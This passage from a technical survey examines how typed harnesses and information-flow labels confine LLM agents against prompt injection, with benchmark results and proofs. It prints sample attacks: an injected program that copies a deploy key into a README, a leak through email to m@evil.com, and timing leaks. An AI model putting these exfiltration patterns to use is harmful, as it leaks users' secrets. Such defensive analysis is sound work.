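To test the implementation, Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent called Nomo in ETAS. Nomo has 7,671 lines of code, and the test covered 1,417 lines around the part that decides which files to read or search. Handlers supplied fixed replies in place of a live model and real tools. The program completed 4 of the 10 scenarios and stopped at the expected point in the other 6. The handlers dealt correctly with all 19 requests.

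Those requests consisted of 12 model calls, 5 file reads and 2 searches. None was a write or an approval, so the scenarios do not test the rule about asking before writing. Six short programs, separate from Nomo, do:

| Program | Compiler's decision |
|---|---|
| approval request, then write | accepted |
| the same, with a dry-run handler | accepted |
| no approval request | rejected |
| approval request after the write | rejected |
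| forbidden write, intercepted by a handler | rejected |
| write outside the declared row | rejected |

These results show that the compiler implements the main checks and that a handler does not hide a forbidden write from it. They provide little evidence of how often the compiler makes mistakes on larger programs. The researchers chose the four faulty programs themselves, each with a single known error, and no model or attacker tried to get around the checks.

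The six programs also don't test the residual monitor, because the compiler accepted or rejected each of them outright. It was stricter about the forbidden write than the formal rules, which could have left the decision to a monitor. Its error message for a missing approval suggests that it requires an approval request on every path to the write, so it might also reject the `if urgent` program. None of the tests mixes good and bad paths in this way.

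Tan and colleagues tested a separate Python model of the contracts much more thoroughly. They generated 384 contracts and ran each against all 1,093 possible sequences of up to six approvals, writes and reads. All 419,712 results agreed with a direct check of the rules. Twelve further cases covered all three outcomes, including the residual monitor. This is good evidence that the translation from clauses to automata is right, but only indirect evidence about the compiler, which is a different program written in Rust.

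### Harnesses that revise themselves

The checks can also apply to changes in the harness. Some agents use feedback from earlier tasks to rewrite their own prompts, choice of tools or code for processing results. In ETAS, a supervisor fixes the harness's input and output types, its row, its trace contract and the host operations it can reach. Each revision and any code it depends on must compile against these limits before the revision runs, and a revision cannot loosen them by declaring a wider row. If the compiler rejects a revision, the error messages can guide the next attempt.

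Tan and colleagues put a harness for financial questions through five generations of revisions, and its accuracy on 256 questions rose from 69.9% (179 correct) to 78.9% (202 correct). A second harness, for patent questions, improved from 30% to 72% on 50 questions. The financial harness grew from 8 lines of code to 58, mostly in the prompt and in the functions that read data and organise the reasoning.

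The gains show that a harness can improve a good deal while its limits stay fixed, but they don't show that the limits prevented anything. The paper does not report how many revisions the compiler rejected or whether any would have exceeded the row or the contract. Exceeding them would also do little to help a harness answer questions about financial tables. A test of safety would need tasks where forbidden actions improve results, such as coding tasks that a harness could complete more often by skipping approval.

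Revisions can also change an agent's behaviour in ways that no effect check detects. *Your Agent May Misevolve* (Shao, Ren et al., 2025) studied a coding agent that saved notes on successful strategies. After three rounds on SWE-bench Verified, the agent refused 54.4% of harmful coding requests, down from 99.4%, even though the model was unchanged. In ETAS, such notes would be ordinary text, and the compiler would accept a harness that added them to its prompt. The fixed row and contract would still limit which operations the less cautious agent could carry out, and in what order.

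## Keeping secrets and untrusted text from flowing into actions

An order contract can require approval before a write, but it doesn't limit what the patch contains. Suppose a hostile comment leads the model to write this program for the maintenance agent:

```
let key   = read("secrets/deploy.key") in
let patch = insert(key, "README.md") in
let ok    = ask(patch) in
if ok then write(patch) else ()
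```

The program has the row {Read, Ask, Write} and asks before it writes, so it passes both checks. If the person overlooks one odd line in a long patch, everyone with access to the repository can read the key. The expression `read("secrets/deploy.key")` can leak the key on its own, because the harness puts the result into the model's next prompt, which may go to another company's servers. Odersky and colleagues point out that a sandbox does not prevent this. The agent is allowed to read the file and to contact its model, and the leak comes from moving data from the file to the model.

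Some tasks, such as summarising a confidential incident report, require the agent to read secrets, so the designer cannot always forbid it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes access control as a yes-or-no gate. Information-flow control instead attaches labels to data and follows them through the program. The program can then use a secret, but the labels restrict where anything derived from it may go.

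### Noninterference

Labels for agents usually record secrecy, trust or both. *SPA* (2026) traces the rules for secrecy to the Bell–LaPadula model and those for trust to Biba's. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) gives the simplest version, with two levels of each. With ⊑ for "may flow to", the permitted directions are:

Public ⊑ Secret and Trusted ⊑ Untrusted

A program may write public text to a secret file, but not secret text to a public file. It may mix trusted data into untrusted data, but it may not let untrusted data determine a trusted action such as a payment. When a program combines two pieces of data, the result gets the lowest label that both may flow to, written with ⊔. For example, Public ⊔ Secret = Secret.

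The usual goal is noninterference. For secrecy, this means that a program's public outputs do not depend on its secret inputs. If two runs with the same public inputs but different secrets can produce different public outputs, the program leaks. *Cryptographically Secure Information Flow Control on Key-Value Stores* (2017) gives the corresponding definition for trust: an attacker who controls the untrusted inputs cannot influence the trusted outputs.

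Noninterference also rules out leaks that copy nothing:

```
if firstLetter(key) = "a" then ask(patch1) else ask(patch2)
```

Neither patch contains any part of the key, but anyone who sees the request learns something about the key's first letter. A trace contract cannot express noninterference because it is checked against one run at a time, and noninterference is a relation between two runs.

### Classified data in TACIT

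TACIT protects secrets with a wrapper type called Classified. The user designates certain folders as classified, and a program that reads a file there receives a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. The two most important operations, slightly simplified, are:

```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
  def reveal(using CanAccess[T]): T
```

The `reveal` operation returns the unwrapped content, but it requires a capability that the agent does not have. The agent can use `map` to apply a function to the content, but the result stays wrapped. The arrow `->` requires that function to be pure.

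The checker accepts this program, which leaves out the surrounding block that grants file access:

```
val key    = readClassified("secrets/deploy.key")
val length = key.map(text => text.length)
println(length)
```

The function only counts characters, so it has the type `String -> Int`, and `length` has the type `Classified[Int]`. Now suppose that `out` is a capability for an ordinary file and the model writes:

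```
key.map(text => out.write(text))
```

The checker rejects this program in three steps:

1. The function uses `out`, so its type is `String ->{out} Unit`.
2. The `map` operation requires a function of type `String -> U`, which may hold no capabilities.
3. The set {out} is not a subset of the empty set, so the types do not match.

The same rule prevents the function from contacting a server or storing the key in an outside variable. Code outside `map` cannot branch on the key either, because it never has the unwrapped text.

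Printing is safe because TACIT has two output channels. In the accepted program, `println(length)` shows the actual number on the user's terminal, but the agent's model receives only `Classified(****)`. The wrapper persists between snippets in a session, so a later snippet can compute with `length` without exposing the number to the model.

Some tasks require a model to process the secret text. For these, TACIT provides a `chat` function, which sends the text to a second model that the user trusts, usually one running locally. `chat` takes a `Classified[String]` and returns another `Classified[String]`. The agent can therefore have a confidential contract summarised and save the summary in a classified file without either text reaching its own model. The types guarantee that `chat` receives no capabilities, but they cannot guarantee that the service behind it doesn't retain the text, so the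 operator has to ensure this.

The wrapper protects secrets but does little about untrusted text. A hostile comment in an ordinary source file still reaches the agent's model, which may then propose a bad patch. LACUNA has the same limit, as Zhao and colleagues acknowledge.

Odersky and colleagues tested the wrapper on a sample software project whose secrets folder held access keys, a database and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, some of which posed as system messages or contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In 11 further trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or impersonated someone with authority. This made 131 trials for each model, with and without the wrapper. The table shows the percentage of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output, and the percentage of the 120 ordinary trials in which the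 agent completed its task:

| Model | No leak, Classified | No leak, plain text | Tasks completed, Classified | Tasks completed, plain text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100 | 98.5 | 99.2 | 83.3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100 | 91.6 | 90.0 | 88.3 |

Without the wrapper, Claude leaked secrets in two trials, both with an impersonator. MiniMax leaked them in 11 trials, including 8 of the 11 malicious requests. With the wrapper, the agent's program has no direct way to obtain the text, so the perfect scores mainly show that the implementation has no obvious holes. The attacks tried to persuade the model and did not search for bugs in the library. The test also counted only secret text in the output, so it would have missed a leak through timing.

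Claude completed more tasks with the wrapper than without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest the difference may be an artifact of the setup, because Claude often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

### Labels that rise in ELBA

ELBA uses an existing Haskell library for information-flow control, LIO, which Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, describe in detail. LIO keeps a current label for the running program, which covers everything the program has read so far. If L is the current label, there are two main rules:

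- Reading data with label l changes the current label to L ⊔ l.
- Writing to a destination with label l requires L ⊑ l.

If the maintenance agent used LIO, the program that puts a key into the README file would run as follows, assuming that the approval request is allowed to show secrets:

| Step | Label before | Check | Label after |
|---|---|---|---|
| read the key | Public | none | Public ⊔ Secret = Secret |
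| ask for approval | Secret | Secret ⊑ Secret holds | Secret |
| write to the README | Secret | Secret ⊑ Public fails | the program gets an error |

The same method works for trust. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a program downloads a page from phony.com and then tries to write to a destination reserved for the user's own data. The download lowers the program's trust level to that of phony.com, so the write fails.

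LIO makes these checks while the program runs, and the type checker stops programs from avoiding them. ELBA requires the agent's program to have the type `DC ()`, where DC is LIO's effect type with labels for both secrecy and trust. As with `BibIO ()`, this type rules out direct calls to functions such as `writeFile`, so every file or network operation has to go through LIO. But a program that passes the type check can still fail a policy check halfway through, after earlier steps have taken effect. TACIT checks programs before running them, so the one that tries to write out a key never starts.

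A single label for the whole program is also crude. LIO uses the current label to protect all values in scope that have no label of their own (*On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, 2015), so once the maintenance agent has read the key, it cannot write any patch to a public file, even a patch unrelated to the key.

LIO's function `toLabeled` avoids this by running part of a program separately. The current label can rise inside that part, but the outer program keeps its old label and receives the result in a wrapper. Zhou and colleagues give the example of an agent that has a sub-agent write a direct message. The sub-agent may read untrusted text and call tools, subject to the label checks. The outer agent passes the wrapped message to a sending function with this type:

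```
sendDM :: User -> Labeled DCLabel Message -> DC ()
```

The function checks the message's label against the recipient, so the outer agent can send the message without reading it.

The program must choose the wrapper's label before the separate part runs, because a label that depended on what that part read could reveal a secret. For example, a program could read one file if a password began with "a" and a different file otherwise, and the label would show which one it read. If the separate part reads something above the chosen label, the wrapper contains an error instead of a result.

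LIO's wrapper has no operation like TACIT's `map`. Stefan and colleagues note that such an operation would violate noninterference once labels record trust. `map` is safe for secrecy because applying a function to a secret produces something no more secret than the original. But if `approved` contains a patch that a person has approved, and the agent writes `approved.map(x => otherPatch)`, the wrapper would mark as approved a patch that the person never saw.

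### The cost of ELBA's policies

Zhou and colleagues' forced-injection test, in which a sub-agent receives the attacker's text as its whole prompt, used AgentDojo's tasks for the messaging service Slack. The 735 attempts per model were seven runs of 105 combinations of a user's task and an attack:

| Model | Attacks resisted, no policies | Attacks resisted, policies | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, policies |
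|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT-5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted 29 of the 2,940 attempts with policies as successful attacks, because the agent had opened a particular web address. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found no violation, since opening the address sent no private data.

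The policies reduced the completion rate by 23 to 33 percentage points. They lower a program's permissions to the level of the least trusted source it has read, but many ordinary requests require a program to read untrusted text and then take an action that needs higher permissions. For example, a user who asks an agent to pay the bill described in a file wants the file's text to determine a payment, and a label check cannot distinguish this from an attack.

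Zhou and colleagues argue that a strict filter is still useful when a person is available. The agent can carry out permitted actions without asking, and the person only has to decide about the rest. But if a quarter of legitimate tasks still need a decision, the person may tire of answering, as with other approval requests.

### Comparisons with CaMeL

CaMeL also tracks labels at run time, but it divides the work between two models, an arrangement that the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model writes a program to carry out the user's request without reading any untrusted data. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and returns values, but cannot call tools. A special interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from and checks those origins before each tool call.

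The separation keeps untrusted text from changing the plan and helps keep labels from rising. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) observes that a single untrusted tool result restricts every later tool call if it enters the agent's conversation. The paper's system, FIDES, therefore stores a result in a variable whenever showing it to the planning model would raise the conversation's label. Under CaMeL's design, however, the program cannot adapt freely to what it finds. Odersky and colleagues add that CaMeL's version of Python does not let programs define their own functions.

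On the Slack tasks without attacks, Zhou and colleagues found that with policies in force, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of 21 tasks, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 4 to 6. Without policies, ELBA completed 14 to 18 and CaMeL 13 to 17. Letting agents react to data seems to help most when policies are strict, although 21 tasks is a small sample. Under attack, with 105 combinations per setting, ELBA's advantage with policies was also about twofold for most models.

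Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with CaMeL on all four of AgentDojo's suites, using published figures for CaMeL. These are the percentages of tasks completed:

| Suite | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini-high, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8 | 56.9 | 62.5 | 59.0 |
| Workspace | 53.8 | 50.5 | 81.4 | 52.9 |
| Slack | 48.6 | 40.0 | 68.6 | 47.6 |
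| Travel | 1.4 | 64.3 | 74.3 | 68.6 |

They describe the results of TACIT and CaMeL as comparable, but the figures for o4-mini-high do not fit this description. With that model, TACIT completed 52.86% of workspace tasks and CaMeL completed 81.4%. On Slack tasks, the gap was 21 points.

CaMeL's 1.4% on travel tasks with Gemini, or two successes in 140 trials, is also suspicious, since the same system completed 74.3% with o4-mini-high. Odersky and colleagues do not explain the figure, which may reflect a technical failure with one model or a mistake in the data. Averaged over all eight pairs, TACIT is only 0.4 points behind CaMeL. Without the Gemini travel result, it is 9.5 points behind and ahead in only one of seven pairs.

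Both systems blocked nearly every attack. TACIT's only recorded failure was on a travel task where the attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in some reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because the quotes included the other hotel's name.

These security scores are weaker evidence than they appear. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands sorted the 144 combinations of task and attack in the banking suite. In 97 of them, the attack needed a tool or file that a program for the user's task would never use, so writing the program in advance was generally enough to stop it. Only the other 47 tested the control of data. They argue that TACIT and ELBA rely entirely on their types in all 144 cases, because agents in those systems read data before writing more code. But the models' own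 resistance also affects the scores, since Zhou and colleagues' models resisted every ordinary Slack attack without policies. The forced-injection test is much better evidence because it removes that resistance.

### A noninterference theorem for agents

Tracking labels at run time is easy to get wrong. Garby, Gordon and Sands found that CaMeL's interpreter can leak a secret through a branch that does not run. A program of this kind could reveal whether a bank balance is above some limit:

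```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > limit: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the limit. The third line sets `tmp` to False and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays True and keeps its public label. Because the condition on the last line is public, the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is below the limit, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out. The email therefore reveals the secret, although the interpreter never detected a secret value reaching it.

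LIO blocks this program because reading the balance raises the label of everything that follows. In TACIT, the balance would be in a wrapper, and a function passed to `map` could not change `tmp`.

Garby, Gordon and Sands designed a small programming language, LLMbda, to prevent such leaks in general. It labels each value and also the conversation with the model. If a secret determines whether the program adds a message to a public conversation, LLMbda stops the program, because the model's later answers could reveal which branch ran. Labelling the conversation also avoids a problem that Odersky and colleagues attribute to run-time tracking in general, which is that a value loses its label once it enters a model's context. Only systems that leave the context unlabelled have this problem.

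A model's answers vary, so the theorem about LLMbda compares probabilities. Take two inputs that differ only in their secrets. Let μ₀(q) and μ₁(q) be the probabilities that someone who sees only public data observes the outcome q. These probabilities can add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish and a label check may stop others. The theorem states that there is a single function ω such that:

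μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q, and the sum of all ω(q) is at most 1.

For example, one secret might make the program answer "yes" in 60% of runs and never finish in the rest, while another makes it answer "yes" in 80%. The theorem allows this, with ω("yes") = 0.8. It does not allow one secret to give "yes" in 70% of runs and the other to give "no" in 70%, because ω would then add up to 1.4, which is over the limit of 1. If the program always finishes, μ₀ and μ₁ each add up to 1 already, so they must be equal.

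The proof constructs ω by running a modified version of the program that skips any computation whose label becomes secret and substitutes an empty value. The secrets then make no difference, so both inputs give the same ω. Skipping computations can't make the program less likely to finish, so ω is at least as large as μ₀ and μ₁.

The theorem applies to every LLMbda program, including those a model writes during a run. The proof has been checked with Lean, a system for machine-checked mathematics. The theorem assumes that the data sources are part of the program, and the developer still has to label them correctly.

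### Timing and endless loops

A covert channel is a flow of information through a mechanism that was not meant to carry it, according to *Proving the Absence of Microarchitectural Timing Channels* (2023). Running time is a common example. TACIT's checker accepts this program, where `slow` is a pure function that takes a minute to compute a number:

```
key.map(text => if text.startsWith("a") then slow(text) else 0)
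```

The result stays in its wrapper, but anyone who can measure how long the program took learns whether the key begins with "a". Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee and describe such a leak as a single bit, but an agent that can repeat the test with other letters and positions could recover the whole key. The information-flow proofs for seL4, a heavily verified operating-system kernel, do not cover timing either.

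A program can also leak a secret by looping forever if the secret has a certain value and finishing otherwise. If the harness stops the program after a minute and reports a timeout, the agent learns one bit about the secret. LIO's guarantee and the LLMbda theorem both permit such leaks. A single run leaks little, but Garby, Gordon and Sands found that CaMeL's retry loop makes the leak serious. The loop runs outside the interpreter that tracks labels, and whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret. An attacker could retry with different tests and extract the secret one bit at a time. ELBA retries only programs that fail the type check, not programs that a label check stops.

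LIO's remedy is clearance, an upper limit on the current label. If the limit is Public, an attempt to read a secret fails before the program receives it. The program therefore cannot leak the secret through timing or any other channel, but it cannot use the secret either.

### Deliberate release

Strict noninterference would prevent an agent from revealing anything that depends on a secret, or from acting on anything it reads in an email. Practical systems therefore need exceptions. In TACIT, the user can see classified results on the terminal, and someone with the right capability can unwrap them.

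LLMbda's `endorse` operation marks untrusted data as trusted. In one example, an agent sorts incoming emails with a quarantined model and uses the category as the subject of its reply. The sending tool accepts only trusted subjects, so the program maps the model's answer to one of a few fixed categories and endorses the result. An attacker can still write an email that influences which category the agent picks, but cannot put their own words in the subject line. With eight categories, the attacker controls at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits per email. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing data this way cannot release secrets.

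Garby, Gordon and Sands tested Randori, an agent they wrote in LLMbda, on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs, while CaMeL completed 32 without policies and 18 with them. Endorsement explains part of Randori's advantage. Without it, completed runs fell from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5. CaMeL with policies still completed fewer runs with MiMo-v2.5, at 18. Some of the remaining difference may come from looser rules, since Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies.

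Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded, both in the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Before reading the file, the model had endorsed its text in the program it wrote, as the task required. Without endorsement, the attack fails, but the agent also cannot pay a genuine bill from a file.

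## Unsafe language features and foreign calls

The guarantees described so far assume that a program can perform an effect only if its type records that effect. Most practical languages have escape hatches that break this assumption, and a single use of one can void the guarantees for a whole program.

Suppose a language has a function `hide` that runs a computation and gives the result a pure type. This adds a new rule for effect judgments:

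If Γ ⊢ e : τ ! ε, then Γ ⊢ hide(e) : τ ! ∅.

In the maintenance agent's program, `send(source)` has the effect set {Net}, but `hide(send(source))` has the empty set. The widening rule can enlarge the empty set to any other set, so the checker accepts the second expression whatever effects the harness declares, even though running it uses the network.

`hide` also undermines checks in code that never mentions it. TACIT's `map` passes a secret to any function with a pure type, and a dry-run test treats an empty effect row as proof that the repository is safe. Both would now accept functions that use the network.

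A team of programmers can tolerate unsafe features by agreeing to use them carefully. An untrusted model cannot be relied on to follow such a convention, so the guarantee has to hold for every program the model might write.

### Kinds of escape hatch

An unchecked cast makes the compiler treat a value as having a different type. If a program casts a function of type `Text ->{net} Unit` to `Text -> Unit`, the new type marks the function as pure, but calling it still uses the network. Scala cannot catch this at runtime because capture sets exist only at compile time. Safe subsets therefore forbid casts that the compiler cannot verify.

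Reflection lets a running program look up classes and methods by name and call those methods. The result of such a call has a very general type that does not show which capabilities the method used. A program might also use reflection to call a private constructor and create a capability that nobody granted. Designers prevent both problems by making the reflection functions unavailable.

Some functions give effectful computations the types of pure values. Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` has the type `IO a -> a`, so it is a real version of `hide`. Its result looks like an ordinary value, but computing it can involve any input or output. The compiler also assumes that the value is pure, so the effect may run once, several times or never. ELBA's bibliography agent could use this function to write an invented entry from inside a `BibIO` program. Zhou and colleagues rely on Safe Haskell, GHC's safe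 subset, to exclude `unsafePerformIO`.

A foreign call runs code written in another language, usually C. The programmer declares a name and a type for the C function, and the compiler accepts the declaration without checking the C code. A function declared as `Int -> Int` appears pure, but its C code can do anything the operating system allows the process to do, including overwriting the typed program's memory. Designers can require foreign functions to have the broadest effect type, or restrict foreign calls to trusted libraries.

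Code that runs during compilation also escapes the check. Template Haskell, a GHC extension, runs Haskell code at compile time to generate parts of a program. This code can perform input and output that the finished program's type does not show. A program may therefore act before the compiler rejects it for a type error. Designers disable the feature for untrusted code and run the compiler itself in a sandbox.

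### Safe Haskell

Safe Haskell has been part of GHC since version 7.2. It assigns each module, usually a single source file, one of three trust levels:

| Level | Who vouches for the module | Limits on its code |
|---|---|---|
| Safe | the compiler | only the safe subset and trusted imports |
| Trustworthy | its author | almost none |
| Unsafe | nobody | none |

A Safe module can import Safe and Trustworthy modules but not Unsafe ones. GHC treats an unlabeled module as Safe if it would compile as Safe, and as Unsafe otherwise. In a system like ELBA, the model's program would be Safe, and the library that defines its operations could be Safe or Trustworthy.

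Any author can label a module Trustworthy, so GHC has an option called package trust, under which a Trustworthy module counts as trusted only if the user compiling the program has chosen to trust its package. If a Trustworthy module uses unsafe functions and imports a Safe module from another author's package, the user has to trust only the first author, because the compiler has checked the second author's code. The option is off by default because, with it on, whether a program compiles depends on the settings of each user's machine.

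The safe subset closes or narrows these features:

| Feature | Danger | Treatment in Safe modules |
|---|---|---|
| Template Haskell | can reach private constructors | GHC disables it |
| Foreign calls | a pure type can hide effects | GHC requires an `IO` type |
| Rewrite rules, which replace expressions during optimisation | the replacement may behave differently | GHC ignores them |
| Newtype deriving, which copies operations from a type to a wrapper around it | can bypass private constructors | GHC forbids it |
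| Overlapping instances, which are competing definitions of an operation | an import can change how existing code behaves | GHC rejects unsafe uses |
| Annotations, which attach extra information to code | can bypass the other restrictions | GHC forbids them |

These restrictions make types reliable, but they do not confine a program by themselves. A Safe module can still call `writeFile` or declare a foreign function with an `IO` type. ELBA limits its agent by requiring a result type, such as `BibIO ()`, that rules out running either function. The model also writes a single expression, which in Haskell cannot contain a foreign declaration.

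Safe Haskell does not make compilation safe, because some GHC options start other programs during compilation. GHC's developers recommend compiling untrusted code in a sandbox or under a user account with very limited access. They also recommend setting the Safe level on the command line, where the source code cannot override it.

Safe Haskell's future has been in doubt for years. In April 2021, Richard Eisenberg considered removing it from GHC because it relies on hundreds or perhaps thousands of lines of delicate compiler code. Days later he decided that GHC should renovate it instead, as part of a larger security overhaul. Hécate (2022), in *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?*, raised the question again and pointed to the burden on library authors. Smith (2022) agreed that the drawbacks outweighed the benefits, but replied that limited `IO` types need strict type safety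 to control effects.

In the *Deprecating Safe Haskell* forum thread, a co-author of the original paper thought it plausible to retire the feature because it had not attracted enough users or maintainers. Other participants mentioned that many packages use Template Haskell or unsafe features, and that it is hard to keep Trustworthy code in modules small enough to audit.

GHC still supports Safe Haskell. In May 2026, *Turn `Trustworthy` into `Safe` in `base` where possible* (Jeltsch, 2026) changed the safety level of five standard library modules, so the compiler now checks code that its authors previously only asserted was safe. ELBA can use the feature today, but it has few users, so fewer people probably look for holes in it.

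### Scala's safe mode

Scala's safe mode, which TACIT applies to every snippet, is newer and still experimental. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six restrictions:

| Restriction | Reason |
|---|---|
| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | They can remove capabilities from a value's type. |
| No features from the `caps.unsafe` module | They exempt values from tracking. |
| No `@unchecked` annotations or variants of them | They switch off compiler checks. |
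| No run-time reflection | It bypasses the types. |
| Capture checking on, including for changes to variables | Otherwise a "pure" function could hold a capability. |
| Global objects only if their own code is safe | Otherwise a library call could have untracked effects. |

The compiler has a built-in list of the parts of the standard library it assumes are safe. The list includes Java's `Class`, for example, but not its reflection methods. It omits the global print functions, so a program in safe mode cannot print its result unless a library provides a way. This is stricter than Safe Haskell, which leaves `IO` available and relies on the program's required type to exclude it.

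The last restriction covers only global objects, so a harness can still pass the program a capability from any module, safe or unsafe. The capability's designer has to make sure its methods do not allow too much.

The list does not include native code or Scala's macros, which run code during compilation. The last restriction should prevent a snippet from using most libraries that contain native code. A harness designer would have to test whether safe mode blocks macros, or run the compiler in a sandbox as GHC's developers recommend.

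### Why libraries need unsafe code

Some trusted code has to carry out file writes and network requests, and a safe subset omits these operations or hides them behind narrower types. Other libraries use unsafe features for speed. Terei, Marlow and colleagues (2012), who introduced GHC's safe subset, give the example of ByteString, a widely used library that stores text compactly and reads it directly from memory. Its functions behave as pure functions even though their implementation is unsafe. A participant in the forum thread mentions a C library for text patterns. Preparing a pattern with it has no visible side effects, but the Haskell compiler cannot confirm this.

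Both languages therefore let a library's author vouch for code that the compiler cannot check. Haskell uses the Trustworthy label, and Scala uses the `@assumeSafe` annotation. VirtusLab, a software consultancy, notes that safe mode forbids this annotation in the program itself, since the model could otherwise vouch for its own code. A library author can also use `@rejectSafe` to hide selected parts of a trusted component from programs in safe mode.

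### A cached function

Scala's developers illustrate `@assumeSafe` with a class that remembers the results of a slow function. This class does the same job:

```
@assumeSafe
class Cache[In, Out](f: In -> Out):
  @untrackedCaptures
  private val table = HashMap[In, Out]()
  def apply(x: In): Out =
    table.get(x) match
      case Some(known) => known
      case None =>
        val y = f(x)
        table.put(x, y)
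        y
```

The first call with an argument `x` computes `f(x)` and stores the result in `table`. Later calls with `x` return the stored result.

The table is mutable, so capture checking treats it as a capability. A `Cache` value would therefore not be pure, and a program could not use one inside `map` on classified data. Scala's *unsafe* documents the annotation `@untrackedCaptures`, which leaves the table out of the value's capture set. The annotation comes from `caps.unsafe`, so a `Cache` class that uses it could not compile in safe mode.

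The author now has to prove what the compiler no longer checks, namely that the table makes no observable difference to the program's results. Scala's developers name two conditions. The table must contain only results of earlier calls, and `f` must be referentially transparent, meaning that repeating a call with the same argument gives the same result. The main step is to show that this statement always holds:

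for every entry (x, y) in the table, y = f(x)

It holds at the start because the table is empty. The only line that changes the table adds the pair (x, f(x)), and `private` prevents other code from adding entries. The type `In -> Out` helps with the second condition, because `f` cannot hold a capability for something that changes, such as a file.

The proof also needs a condition that Scala's developers do not mention. The table looks up entries using the equality test for the argument's type, and a program can define that test. If the test treats two different arguments as equal, the second call may return the first call's result. The table could then carry information from one call to another, including out of a function that was processing a secret. An author could prevent this by allowing only types with a reliable equality test, such as `String`.

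The author can do the verification informally, as here, or with a proof assistant. Odersky and colleagues cite RustBelt, a formal treatment of the similar boundary between safe and unsafe code in Rust, as evidence that such proofs are possible.

An `@assumeSafe` object can also permit a visible effect under certain conditions. In another example from Scala's developers, the `CheckedMailer` object shows each email to the user and sends it only if the user confirms. The agent's program cannot access the ordinary mailer behind it. The maintenance agent's `write` operation could work the same way, showing each patch to a person before applying it.

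However, the function in this example takes no capability, so the checker would apparently treat code that calls it as pure. A program could then call it from inside `map` on a secret, and the user's confirmation would be the only remaining protection. Requiring a capability such as `IOCapability`, as TACIT's own functions do, would prevent this.

### Exceptions

An exception is also an effect, and it can leak information. For example, a function that processes a secret could put it in an error message and then stop the program. Safe mode still allows exceptions because tracking every possible error in types would be impractical.

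The harness contains exceptions at run time with Scala's `Try`, which returns a failure value when the code inside it throws an exception. If the code was processing classified data, the harness can put the failure value into a `Classified` wrapper so that the agent's model does not see the error message. The compiler also prevents exceptions from holding capabilities, so a program cannot use an exception to carry a file permission out of its block. Scala 3 implements other jumps, such as breaks and early returns from nested functions, as exceptions, and Scala's developers rely on the same containment for them.

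The standard `Try` does not catch some serious errors, including running out of memory, so a harness needs another barrier, such as a separate process, to survive them.

### Effect for TypeScript

A library can track effects while leaving the language's unsafe features available. Effect, a library for TypeScript, gives computations types of the form `Effect<A, E, R>`, where `A` is the type of the result, `E` lists the expected errors, and `R` lists the services the computation requires. For example, a computation that writes a patch through a service called `Repo` might have the type `Effect<void, WriteError, Repo>`. A program must supply a `Repo` before it can run the computation, and a test can supply a fake one. The requirements in `R` therefore work much like an effect row.

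But nothing forces a TypeScript program to use these services. The library's function `Effect.sync` turns ordinary code into a computation:

```
const save = Effect.sync(() => writeFileSync("notes.txt", text))
```

A computation that writes a file when run can have the type `Effect<void, never, never>`, where `never` means that it has no expected errors and no requirements. Surrounding code can also call `writeFileSync` directly, without using Effect. TypeScript also has unchecked casts, and its designers explicitly decided not to aim for a sound type system.

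Effect is still useful to programmers for tracking what their own code depends on. To confine an agent, a designer would have to combine Effect with something that removes the other routes to files and the network. VirtusLab mentions running TypeScript inside WebAssembly, which has no input or output unless the host provides it. In that arrangement, WebAssembly limits what the agent can do, and Effect's types mainly help the model write code that fits those limits.

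### The trusted base

Closing the escape hatches still leaves a good deal of software that has to work correctly. Odersky and colleagues list TACIT's trusted components as the Scala compiler, the capability library, the runtime that executes the code and, where a harness uses one, the local model that reads classified text. For typed harnesses in general, the trusted base includes:

- the compiler, from its type checker and safe-subset rules to the part that generates machine code
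- the runtime system and any foreign code it calls
- the libraries that carry out effects, and other libraries whose authors have vouched for them
- the harness code that sets the permitted effects and ensures that the program it runs is the one the compiler checked
- the operating system and the hardware

Zhou and colleagues' whole-system theorem assumes that the language's types guarantee the desired property. If GHC accepts a program that Haskell's rules should reject, the theorem no longer applies to ELBA. The guarantee could also fail if GHC checks a program correctly but compiles it wrongly. One participant in the forum thread cites GHC releases that produced wrong arithmetic on Apple's M1 chips.

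### Soundness bugs in compilers

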